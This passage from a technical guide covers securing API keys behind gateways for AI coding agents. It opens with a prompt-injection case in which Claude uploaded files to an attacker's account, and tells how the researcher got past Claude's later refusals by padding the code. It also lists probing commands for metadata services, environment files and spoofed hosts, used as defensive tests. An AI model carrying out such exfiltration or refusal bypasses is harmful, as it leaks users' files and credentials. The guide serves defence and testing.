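3. Claude ran a few lines of Python that set `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` to the attacker's key and uploaded the file with Anthropic's Files API.
4. The file appeared in the attacker's account, where the attacker could open it.

The attacker could upload up to 30 MB at a time and could repeat the upload. The attack worked the first time, but Claude then began to refuse, apparently because a visible API key looked suspicious. The researcher got past this by adding harmless code, such as a line that prints "Hello, world".

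Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope, but said five days later that this had been a mistake. In January 2026, the security company PromptArmor used the same method against Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, as Willison reported in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (2026).

The local inference endpoint prevents this attack because the gateway removes the caller's key. But this works only for requests that go through the endpoint:

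| Where the agent sends the upload | What happens to the attacker's key | Result |
|---|---|---|
| The local inference endpoint, with only model paths permitted | The gateway never forwards it | The gateway rejects the upload |
| The local inference endpoint, with every path permitted | The gateway replaces it with the operator's key | The file goes to the operator's account |
| `api.anthropic.com`, which the egress rules allow | It reaches Anthropic unchanged | The file goes to the attacker's account |
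| `api.anthropic.com`, which the egress rules block | It never leaves the sandbox | The upload fails |

The attack succeeds in the third row even if the operator has set up the gateway correctly. An ordinary egress rule checks the server's name, which is correct, but can't check the key because it is inside the encrypted request. This is why NVIDIA advises keeping model providers' hosts out of OpenShell's network policy.

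Cowork has to contact `api.anthropic.com`, so Anthropic couldn't block that address. Instead, Anthropic added a proxy inside Cowork's virtual machine that decrypts requests to the API and forwards only those with the session token Anthropic gave that machine. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something. Embrace The Red had proposed much the same fix, a sandbox that lets Claude contact only the logged-in user's account.

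Rejecting a foreign key makes an attack easier to detect than silently replacing the key does. The agent has no ordinary reason to send a second valid key, so a rejection is a strong sign of an attack and the gateway can alert someone. If the gateway replaces the key without recording it, the operator may never learn of the attempt. A gateway can accept only the placeholder or gateway token it expects, reject requests that carry any other key, and log those attempts without recording the key itself.

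Anthropic now treats allowing a domain as allowing everything the domain offers. For each service the agent may contact, an operator can ask whether a stranger can have an account there and whether the agent could upload to it.

### Other programs that can reach the gateway

Programs other than the agent may be able to use the gateway. If a gateway on a laptop listens on `localhost:8080` and accepts any request, every program on the laptop can make requests with the key, including programs run by other users. If it listens on every network interface, other computers may be able to use it too.

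A web page in the developer's browser can also send a request to `localhost`. The browser normally prevents the page from reading the reply, but by then the gateway may have forwarded the request and the provider may have charged for it. Anthropic has received reports of several flaws in Claude Code caused by trusting local input too early, and it advises treating requests to programs listening on `localhost` as if they came from the internet.

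Operators often leave such services open. Dantuluri and Sundi cite a survey of 7,973 remote MCP servers in which more than 40 per cent offered tools without any authentication. MCP servers differ from model gateways, but their operators also have to decide whether to require authentication.

A gateway token for each sandbox solves most of this. The gateway generates a long random token, gives it to the sandbox, and stores a record with a hash (a fingerprint from which nobody can work out the token):

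```json
{
  "token_sha256": "<hash>",
  "sandbox": "alice-failing-tests",
  "model": "<model-id>",
  "usd_per_day": 20,
  "simultaneous_requests": 4,
  "expires": "2026-12-01T18:00:00Z"
}
```

A request without a valid token fails, so the web page and the other programs can't use the key. The gateway logs the cost of each request with the sandbox's name. The provider's bill may show only a $400 total for the key, but the log shows that $385 of it came from `alice-failing-tests`.

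When the operator revokes a token, the gateway should also stop any responses still in progress for it, since they would otherwise continue and cost money. Cowork uses similar tokens. Each virtual machine has its own session token with limited permissions, which Anthropic can revoke without logging the user out.

A malicious package inside the sandbox can still use the token, and its requests appear in the log under the same name as the agent's. OpenShell's list of permitted programs doesn't stop such a package. OpenShell does detect when a program has been replaced, by comparing the file's hash with one recorded earlier. If two agents need separate records or budgets, they need separate sandboxes.

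### Checking the structure of each request

The gateways described so far check a request's address and headers, and sometimes its model name. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) proposes a stricter broker, prototyped in Rust, that also checks the structure of the request body.

Before sending a request in CapSeal, an agent opens a session over a Unix socket, and the broker gets the calling process's identity from the operating system rather than from the process itself. The agent then asks for a capability, which is permission for one narrow kind of action. In Jin and colleagues' example, the capability allows `POST` requests to `/v1/chat/completions` on one host, with a body that matches a named description. The broker follows its policy to grant the capability, refuse it or require further approval.

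The agent receives a handle, a reference that works only in that session. For each request, the broker checks that:

- the handle hasn't expired and nobody has revoked it
- the agent has calls left in its quota
- the request isn't a copy of an earlier one, using a sequence number, a random value and a timestamp
- the method, host and path match the capability
- the body isn't too large and the headers are on the permitted list
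- the agent hasn't supplied an authorization header of its own
- the body has the permitted structure

If any check fails, the broker refuses the request without using the key.

CapSeal describes permitted bodies in JSON Type Definition, a standard format for listing the fields a document may contain. A simple description of a request to Claude could look like this:

```json
{
  "properties": {
    "model": {"enum": ["<model-id>"]},
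    "max_tokens": {"type": "uint16"},
    "messages": {"elements": {}}
  },
  "optionalProperties": {
    "system": {},
    "stream": {"type": "boolean"},
    "tools": {"elements": {"properties": {
      "name": {"type": "string"},
      "description": {"type": "string"},
      "input_schema": {}
    }}}
  }
}
```

The format allows only the fields that the description lists. Anthropic's web fetch tool has a `type` field, which isn't listed under `tools`, so the broker would reject a request that includes the tool. It would also reject a request with an `api_base` field like the one in LiteLLM's flaw, or with any option that Anthropic adds later.

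The description still has gaps. The empty braces under `messages` accept anything, including an image given as a web address, so a builder would have to describe the messages in detail too. The format also can't set a maximum of 8,000 for `max_tokens`. The nearest type, `uint16`, allows 65,535, and an answer of that length from Opus 5.5 costs $1.31. CapSeal's quota limits only the number of calls, so an operator also needs a spending cap, because 100 calls could produce $131 of output.

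The agent also proposes the limits of its own capability. A hijacked agent can ask for the widest capability available, so the protection depends on how strict the operator's policy is. Jin and colleagues don't try to protect against someone with administrator rights on the machine.

CapSeal would be hard to put in front of an existing coding agent. It offers its functions to agents as MCP tools, but Claude Code sends its model requests over HTTP and needs a model before it can use any tool. A builder is more likely to copy CapSeal's checks into an ordinary gateway than to install CapSeal. The section "Testing that the agent cannot obtain the key" covers Jin and colleagues' measurements.

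### Signed tokens that can only lose permissions

Some agents start helper agents and give them part of the work. If the main agent passes on its own gateway token, each helper can do everything the main agent can. Dantuluri and Sundi designed a broker that gives each helper a weaker token instead.

Suppose the main agent's token permits Opus 5.5 and $20 of spending until six o'clock. To have a helper summarise a log file, the agent requests a second token from the broker that permits only Claude Haiku 5.5, a much cheaper model, with $1 of spending for ten minutes. The broker adds these restrictions to the existing ones and signs the result with a secret that only it has. The helper can't remove a restriction, because the signature would no longer match. It can request a token for a helper of its own, but that token must be more restricted still. The broker also ties each token to the identity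 of the program meant to use it. If the operator revokes the main agent's token, the helpers' tokens stop working too.

The models and prices are an adaptation to a model gateway. Dantuluri and Sundi's own broker, about 160 lines of Python, controls abstract pairs of tools and resources. They tested it against four threats and compared it with a basic agent program that gives every helper the same powerful token and lets the model decide what to allow:

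| Threat | What the attacker does | Basic program | Broker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Confused deputy | Misleads an agent into misusing its authority | Attack succeeds | Attack fails |
| Stolen token | Uses a copied token from another program | Attack succeeds | Attack fails |
| Privilege escalation | Has the agent use permissions its task doesn't need | Attack succeeds | Attack fails |
| Compromised helper | Takes over a helper agent | Attack succeeds | Attack fails |

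The broker also withstood 11 attacks on its own design, such as removing a restriction or using an expired token, and accepted none of 200,000 forged tokens. In 2,000 random scenarios, a compromised helper could perform 1.5 actions on average, compared with all 8,100 in the basic program. Each check took about 2.6 microseconds, which is negligible compared with the time a model call takes.

In a confused deputy attack, a token with few permissions stops an attacker who wants something outside those permissions, but it can't stop misuse that the token allows. An agent behind a model gateway has to be allowed to call the model. If instructions in a README lead the agent to spend its $20 on the attacker's questions, the broker approves every request because each one is within the token's limits.

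The other results mostly confirm that the code works as designed. Nobody can forge a correctly signed token by guessing, so 200,000 random attempts could reveal only a serious programming error. The helper could perform 1.5 actions on average because that was the size of the tasks it received. Dantuluri and Sundi also wrote the basic program themselves and gave it none of the protections they were testing. They used no live model and haven't released the code. They work for VotalAI, which sells a product based on the same principles.

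One of the tests shows that a stolen token works if the attacker can present the victim program's identity. A malicious package may be able to do that in a sandbox where it runs under the same account as the agent.

Their review of existing software is more useful to a builder. They examined LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen, three popular agent frameworks, and found no built-in limits on what a hijacked agent could do with its tools. They checked this by running LangGraph and reading the code of the other two. Anyone building on one of these frameworks has to add the limits outside it.

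### How strict to be

Every limit can also stop legitimate work. If the gateway permits only one model, the agent can't use a cheaper one for small jobs. If it blocks web tools, the agent can't look up documentation through the provider. A strict schema for the request body causes the most trouble, because an update to Claude Code may add a field that the gateway rejects. Every agent then stops until someone changes the schema.

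NVIDIA advises starting OpenShell's request rules in a mode that only logs violations, then enforcing them once they match normal use. The same approach suits checks on request bodies. A spending cap should apply from the first day, since a high cap rarely interferes with normal work.

Asking a person to approve requests is a poor substitute for limits. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved about 93 per cent of permission prompts and paid less attention as they saw more of them. Approval makes more sense for rare decisions, such as raising a sandbox's cap or allowing a new website.

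An operator running a few coding agents with one provider should permit only the model paths, fix the models and options, block tools that run at the provider, and give each sandbox its own token and daily cap. Signed tokens add little here because the gateway can look up each token's limits in its own records and revoke the token immediately. They become useful when agents often create helpers, or when several gateways have to check tokens without sharing a database.

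Describing the whole request body is worth the upkeep when the agent handles confidential data and reads text from strangers. It works best for an agent with a narrow job, such as sorting issues, because its requests always have much the same structure.

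## Testing that the agent cannot obtain the key

A search that finds no key in the sandbox is evidence that the key is absent only if the search could have found a key that was there. *Aegis OS* (Zhao, 2026) describes tests that didn't meet this condition. Aegis OS is a sandbox for coding agents whose proxy swaps a placeholder for the real key (it is not the AEGIS router described earlier). In early tests on Linux, a mount in the wrong order hid the whole workspace from the sandbox. The sandbox seemed to block every attempt to read credentials or write outside the workspace, but the attempts failed because of the mount error, not the defence.

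### Controls and the test key

The operator first creates a test key at the provider, in its own project with a spending limit of a few dollars, and puts it in the gateway in place of the production key, leaving the rest of the configuration unchanged. If the key leaks during a check, whoever obtains it can spend little, and the operator can revoke it without stopping anyone's work.

Before looking for leaks, the operator runs three controls:

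- An ordinary model call from the sandbox succeeds, and the provider's console lists it under the test key. Without this control, a sandbox with no network would pass almost every check. The console entry confirms that the operator will be searching for the right string.
- A request to an unrelated server arrives there without a credential. The operator may have to allow that server in the egress rules for a few minutes, because a blocked request shows nothing about what the proxy would have added.
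- The search finds a planted string. The operator puts 40 random characters in an environment variable, a file and a server's reply, then runs the search that will later look for the key.

Deliberately disabling a protection also helps show that a test works. Zhao made a test build of Aegis OS with a setting to switch off any one of eight protections, then repeated all 80 attacks with each protection off in turn. Without network confinement, all ten attempts to bypass the proxy succeeded. A builder can do the same on a test machine by adding the provider's host to the egress rules and confirming that the direct-route check now fails.

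The search should look for the exact key. *GreyZone* (2026), a framework for attacking agent applications, does this by comparing known credential values with the record of what the agent did. A search for typical prefixes such as `sk-` misses any key with a different format. The search has to run on the host, because a script in the sandbox that contained the key would put it there. If the operator saves the test key in a file that only root can read and collects the evidence in one folder, a single command is enough:

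```shell
sudo grep -raFl -f /root/test-key /srv/test-evidence
```

The command prints the names of matching files but not the key. It finds only exact copies, so the operator should repeat it for the hexadecimal and Base64 forms of the key.

The agent's own account of what it saw isn't evidence. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026), which tests how agents respond to phishing, counts a leak only when a value the agent submitted matches one in its store of fake credentials.

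### The checks in order

The operator runs these checks from the agent's account after the agent has worked for a few minutes, because some credentials reach the disk only after a login.

| Check | What to do | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Environment | Save the output of `env` and every readable `/proc/*/environ` | A placeholder or gateway token, but no test key |
| 2. Files | Copy the sandbox's disk and mounted folders to the host and search them | No match |
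| 3. Process information | Run `ps auxww` and `sudo -n true`, try to open the gateway's `/proc/<pid>/mem`, and look for a Docker socket | No key in any command line, no administrator rights, no access to the memory and no socket |
| 4. Metadata services | Run `curl -m 5 http://169.254.169.254/` | A timeout or refused connection |
| 5. Prepared headers | Point the agent's base URL at a listener inside the sandbox | A placeholder or gateway token |
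| 6. Echo servers | Make the gateway forward to a test server that records and returns each request | The record shows the test key once and none of the agent's own credentials |
| 7. Error paths | Break the request, the upstream and the key in turn | A fixed message without the key |
| 8. Redirects | Have the test server redirect to a second host | The second host receives nothing |
| 9. Logs | Search the gateway's logs, then try to open them from the sandbox | No key in the logs and no access to them |
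| 10. Direct routes | Try to reach the provider and other outside addresses without the gateway | Every attempt fails |
| 11. Revocation | Revoke the gateway token, issue a new one, then revoke the test key at the provider | Only that sandbox loses access, and later every call fails |

#### Inside the sandbox

`docker export` copies a container's disk but leaves out mounted folders, so the operator has to copy those separately. Git compresses old commits, so `grep` won't find a key in them. Saving the output of `git log -p --all` with the other evidence makes their contents searchable.

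The process check matters most when the gateway shares a container or machine with the agent. *Red-Teaming the Agentic Red-Team* (2026), a study of AI systems that carry out penetration tests, found that many agent frameworks run the worker, which executes commands, in the same container as the orchestrator, which has the secrets. Anyone who can run code in the worker can then read the secrets, even though the worker doesn't need them.

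An error such as 401 or 403 from the metadata address counts as a failed test, because it means the sandbox can reach the service, which may accept a request that includes the required session token or header. On a laptop, nothing normally responds at that address, so a timeout there is weak evidence that the sandbox blocks access.

#### Through the gateway

Public echo services exist, but if the proxy is faulty, the test sends a working key to a stranger. This Python script does the same job on the operator's own machine:

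```python
from http.server import BaseHTTPRequestHandler, HTTPServer

class Echo(BaseHTTPRequestHandler):
    def do_POST(self):
        size = int(self.headers.get("Content-Length", 0))
        body = self.rfile.read(size).decode(errors="replace")
        seen = f"{self.path}\n{self.headers}\n{body}\n"
        print(seen, flush=True)            # the operator's record
        self.send_response(200)
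        self.end_headers()
        self.wfile.write(seen.encode())    # what the agent gets back
    do_GET = do_POST

HTTPServer(("0.0.0.0", 9000), Echo).serve_forever()
```

The operator sets the test gateway's upstream to this server and sends a request from the sandbox with two invented keys, one in `Authorization` and one in `x-api-key`. A gateway that accepts only its own token should reject the request. Any other gateway should forward it, and the record should show the test key in the header the provider expects and neither invented key. Because this server repeats the headers it receives, its reply will contain the test key unless the gateway scans replies. That isn't a fault in the gateway, and it gives the operator a good way to test a scanner.

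If the proxy swaps placeholders, the operator should send another request with the placeholder in the body. The record should show it there unchanged.

For the error check, the operator can send invalid JSON, a path outside the permitted list and a body that is too large, then stop the test server halfway through a reply. The operator can also use a key file with a line break in the middle, which may make the gateway's HTTP library quote the key in its error. For the redirect check, the second server needs a different host name, because many HTTP libraries deliberately keep the credential when only the path changes.

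The log check should also cover the gateway's administrative routes. After OpenAI's July incident, GitLab (2026) advised blocking proxy routes that a client never uses, such as those for administration, configuration and token renewal. A request from the sandbox to any of these routes should fail.

#### Around the gateway

To test the direct route, the operator calls the provider from the sandbox with a valid key from a second account, using `curl --noproxy '*'` to ignore the proxy settings. The operator then repeats the call through the gateway to see whether the gateway removes that key. On OpenShell, these calls test both protections that NVIDIA (2026) claims.

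The operator should also give the agent a real task and compare its transcript with the gateway's log. In *aiAuthZ*, Kodathala (2026) tested a gateway that approves tool calls. When two agent runtimes kept their built-in shell, file and web tools, the model used those tools to carry out the sensitive action without going through the gateway. With an inference gateway, a model call that appears in the transcript but not in the log went out by another route.

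DNS, the system that looks up the addresses of servers, needs its own test. The newsletter tl;dr sec describes a sandbox mode for which AWS promised complete isolation but allowed public DNS queries. A researcher used the queries to control the sandbox from outside, and AWS corrected the documentation instead of blocking the queries. To test for this, the operator looks up a random name under a domain they own and checks whether the query reaches the domain's name server. Even without the key, an agent can use DNS to leak source code or an old key that the file check missed.

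#### Revocation

The operator starts a long streamed answer and revokes the sandbox's gateway token while it is streaming. The answer should stop, the sandbox's next request should fail, and a second sandbox should keep working. *Optional Traps* (2026), a study of AI agents attacking a test network, uses a gateway that behaves this way. After an alert, it refuses one client's requests, even with a valid key, while other clients keep their access.

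The operator then gives the sandbox a new token, confirms that the token works, and revokes the test key at the provider. If model calls still succeed after the provider's usual revocation delay, the gateway is using another key, perhaps through a fallback like Docker's global secret.

### Corvic's test of its own vault

Corvic AI makes Corvic Security Vault, which adds credentials to agents' requests. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) reports a test much like this one, run on the vault on 27 September 2026 from inside Corvic's own Python sandbox. All five researchers work for Corvic, so the company was evaluating its own product.

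In Corvic's design, the agent's code names a connector, a stored entry for one outside service, and the vault adds the credential to requests for that service's host. Each experiment used one connector, and Kenney and colleagues set the expected result of every probe in advance.

One experiment used a connector for FRED, the economic data service of the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis. A script checked the environment variables, 12 common credential paths and the places where platforms mount secrets. It tried the AWS and Google metadata services, called FRED, and sent requests to three public echo services and two unrelated APIs.

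The other experiment used a GitHub connector. The script called a GitHub address that requires a login, inspected the headers it had prepared, and scanned the environment for credentials. It also contacted two echo services and OpenAI's API.

| Control domain | Probes | As expected |
|---|---|---|
| Credential added only for the right host | 5 | 5 |
| Process environment | 2 | 2 |
| Mounted files | 2 | 2 |
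| No disclosure to other servers | 2 | 2 |
| Credential invisible to the calling code | 2 | 2 |
| Cloud metadata blocked | 2 | 2 |
| Authorised call works | 1 | 1 |
| Total | 16 | 16 |

GitHub accepted the request and returned the account's identity, although the script had supplied no credential. None of the sandbox's 20 environment variables looked like a secret, and none of the 12 paths existed. Both metadata services timed out after six seconds. The echo services returned no credential, and OpenAI rejected the calls because they contained none.

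The FRED call failed because the connector was set to send the key in an `Authorization` header, but FRED takes it as a parameter in the web address. FRED therefore returned an error for a missing key. Kenney and colleagues scored connector function separately from security, so this failure isn't among the 16 results. They conclude that keeping credentials in one place doesn't ensure that each one is set up correctly.

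The failure also weakens the other results from that experiment. FRED's reply shows that the network worked, but not that the vault had sent a key. Only this experiment included the file and metadata probes. The script also recognised credentials by common prefixes, so it would probably have missed a FRED key, which is 32 lower-case letters and digits with no prefix. The GitHub experiment is better evidence because its authorised call worked.

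Kenney and colleagues also scored eight threats before and after adding the vault. They multiplied likelihood by impact, each on a scale from 1 to 5:

| Threat | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| User pastes a secret into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Prompt injection through material the agent reads | 25 | 12 |
| Credential sent to the wrong server | 20 | 4 |
| Credential found in the sandbox | 20 | 4 |
| Connector with too many permissions | 20 | 15 |
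| Reuse of a stolen long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through logs or errors | 16 | 8 |
| Wrongly configured connector | 9 | 6 |

These scores are the researchers' judgement and are meant only for setting priorities. The experiments can't support some of them. For example, the score for logs and errors halves, although no probe examined the vault's logs. The two highest remaining scores are for excessive permissions and prompt injection. A vault doesn't reduce what a credential permits or stop an attacker from steering the agent.

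Kenney and colleagues didn't test redirects, OAuth token renewal, MCP sessions, browser tools or a hostile server at the permitted address. They also didn't test DNS rebinding, in which an attacker's website changes its address so that a visitor's browser connects to a local server. They didn't verify how the vault encrypts stored keys, separates customers or replaces credentials, and they report no repeated or simultaneous trials.

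### CapSeal's comparison with direct access

Jin and colleagues compared their broker, CapSeal, with two setups (B1 and B2) that gave the agent the secret directly. They used scripts with fixed prompts to try to reveal an API key or SSH key, make a request outside the permitted limits, and complete a legitimate task.

| Share of trials | B1 | B2 | CapSeal |
|---|---|---|---|
| API key leaked over HTTP | 1.000 | 1.000 | 0.000 |
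| SSH key leaked | 0.000 | 0.000 | 0.000 |
| Unauthorised use succeeded, HTTP or SSH | 0.000 | 0.000 | 0.000 |
| Legitimate task completed | 1.000 | 1.000 | 1.000 |

CapSeal did better than the other setups only in the HTTP leakage test. That result shows that the test could detect a leak and that the broker stopped one. No setup leaked an SSH key or allowed unauthorised use, so those tests can't show that CapSeal helps prevent either. To show that CapSeal reduces unauthorised use, Jin and colleagues would need an attack that succeeds against B1 or B2 and fails against CapSeal.

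The broker added little delay. It raised the median time for an HTTP call to a local server by 0.149 ms, from 0.160 ms to 0.309 ms, over 500 measured calls per system. It raised the median for an SSH command by 0.208 ms, from 7.470 ms to 7.678 ms. The added HTTP delay is less than 0.01 per cent of the two seconds a model might take to answer. Kodathala's figure of at most 0.03 ms covers only the decision to allow a call.

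These benchmarks used small local requests, so they wouldn't show whether a gateway holds back a streamed answer until it is complete. A builder should measure the time until the first piece of an answer arrives, with and without the gateway, while running as many sandboxes as in normal use.

### What zero failures prove

Finding no leaks in 100 trials doesn't mean that the chance of a leak is zero. The Wilson interval, a standard estimate of the range in which the true rate plausibly lies, gives this 95 per cent upper bound when *n* trials produce no failures:

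upper bound = 3.84 / (*n* + 3.84)

| Trials without a failure | Upper bound on the failure rate |
|---|---|
| 16 | 19.4% |
| 80 | 4.6% |
| 100 | 3.7% |
| 381 | 1.0% |
| 1,000 | 0.4% |

Jin and colleagues report an upper bound of 0.037 on the rate of unauthorised use, which corresponds to 100 trials. Even a low rate can matter, because an attacker can keep trying. If each attempt has a 1 per cent chance of success, an attacker who makes 100 independent attempts has a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once.

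The formula assumes the trials are independent and resemble the attacks the system will face. Corvic's 16 probes were different checks chosen by hand, and Kenney and colleagues say no confidence interval is meaningful for them. Running one script 100 times against a gateway that always responds the same way is little better than running it once. Repetition helps when the result can vary, for instance because a model words its answer differently or the provider splits the stream at a different point.

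A scripted trial also provides little evidence about an adaptive attacker, who reads each refusal and tries something else. Aegis OS blocked all 80 of Zhao's attacks, but Zhao wrote those attacks to test the defences he had built. He acknowledges that the result doesn't rule out a bypass he hadn't thought of.

### Adaptive and outside tests

A builder can use an AI agent as an adaptive attacker, as *Optional Traps* does. Its agents attack a mock service whose debugging page leaks a real service key. The agents have limits on requests, model turns, tokens and time. The target's own records determine whether an attack succeeded.

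To test a gateway this way, the builder can give a capable model a shell in the test sandbox, tell it to obtain the test key, and score the result with the search on the host. A planted weakness, such as a deliberately exposed debugging page, is useful here too, because if the model can't find it, its failure to get the key is only weak evidence that the gateway is secure. OpenAI's July incident is a good reason to run this test on a machine with no route to production systems or the internet except the model API. The attacking model should reach that API with a separate capped key.

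Outside researchers have tested some of the software around these gateways. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) compares OpenClaw with two more restrictive versions, including NemoClaw. NemoClaw runs its gateway and the program that executes the agent's tools under different accounts. The overall effect on attacks was only a few percentage points, but that figure doesn't measure how well the separate accounts protect a key.

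Oasis Security found a flaw in NemoClaw that tests from inside the sandbox would have missed. One visit to a malicious website could give an attacker control of the local model server behind NemoClaw, according to SiliconANGLE's *Nvidia NemoClaw flaw let attackers poison the model*. The attack used DNS rebinding, and NVIDIA fixed the flaw on 25 August 2026, as eSecurity Planet's *NVIDIA Patches High-Severity NemoClaw Flaw After Model-Poisoning Demo* (2026) reports. A builder whose gateway listens on a local port can test for this weakness by sending a request from the host with the header `Host: attacker.example`, which the gateway should reject.

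Another company, Cyera, found a flaw in OpenClaw's OpenShell sandbox backend that let attackers write files outside the permitted folder, according to The Hacker News' *Four OpenClaw Flaws Enable Data Theft, Privilege Escalation, and Persistence* (2026). Builders can try more attacks based on these findings, but the findings don't include an independent estimate of how often an attacker could get a provider key out of a gateway.

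### When a build passes and when to test again

A build passes only if it meets all of these conditions:

- The three controls give the expected results.
- The search finds no copy of the test key in the sandbox, the agent's transcript or the gateway's logs. The reply from the echo server is the only exception.
- The test server receives the test key and no foreign key, and the redirect target receives no request.
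- Every direct route fails, including DNS.
- Revoking the gateway token stops the sandbox's requests, including any answer in progress.
- The adaptive attacker finds the planted weakness but doesn't obtain the key.

Every check must pass, because an attacker needs only one leak to get the key. If a check fails, the operator fixes the cause, creates a new test key and repeats the whole procedure, since the fix may have broken something else. An inconclusive result, such as a timeout when the control call also timed out, doesn't count as a pass.

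After the test passes, the operator puts the production key in the gateway, repeats the control call and searches the sandbox again, this time for the production key.

| Event | What to repeat |
|---|---|
| New version of the gateway or its HTTP library | Everything |
| New version of the sandbox software, container image or host kernel | Controls and checks 1 to 4 and 10 |
| New version of the agent, or a new tool for it | Controls and checks 1, 2, 5 and 10 |
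| New provider, upstream address or permitted path | Controls and checks 6 to 10 |
| New mounted folder or egress rule | Controls and checks 2, 3 and 10 |
| Replacement of the production key | The control call, a search for the new key, and a call with the old key, which should fail |
| Published flaw in any of these components | Everything, after installing the fix |
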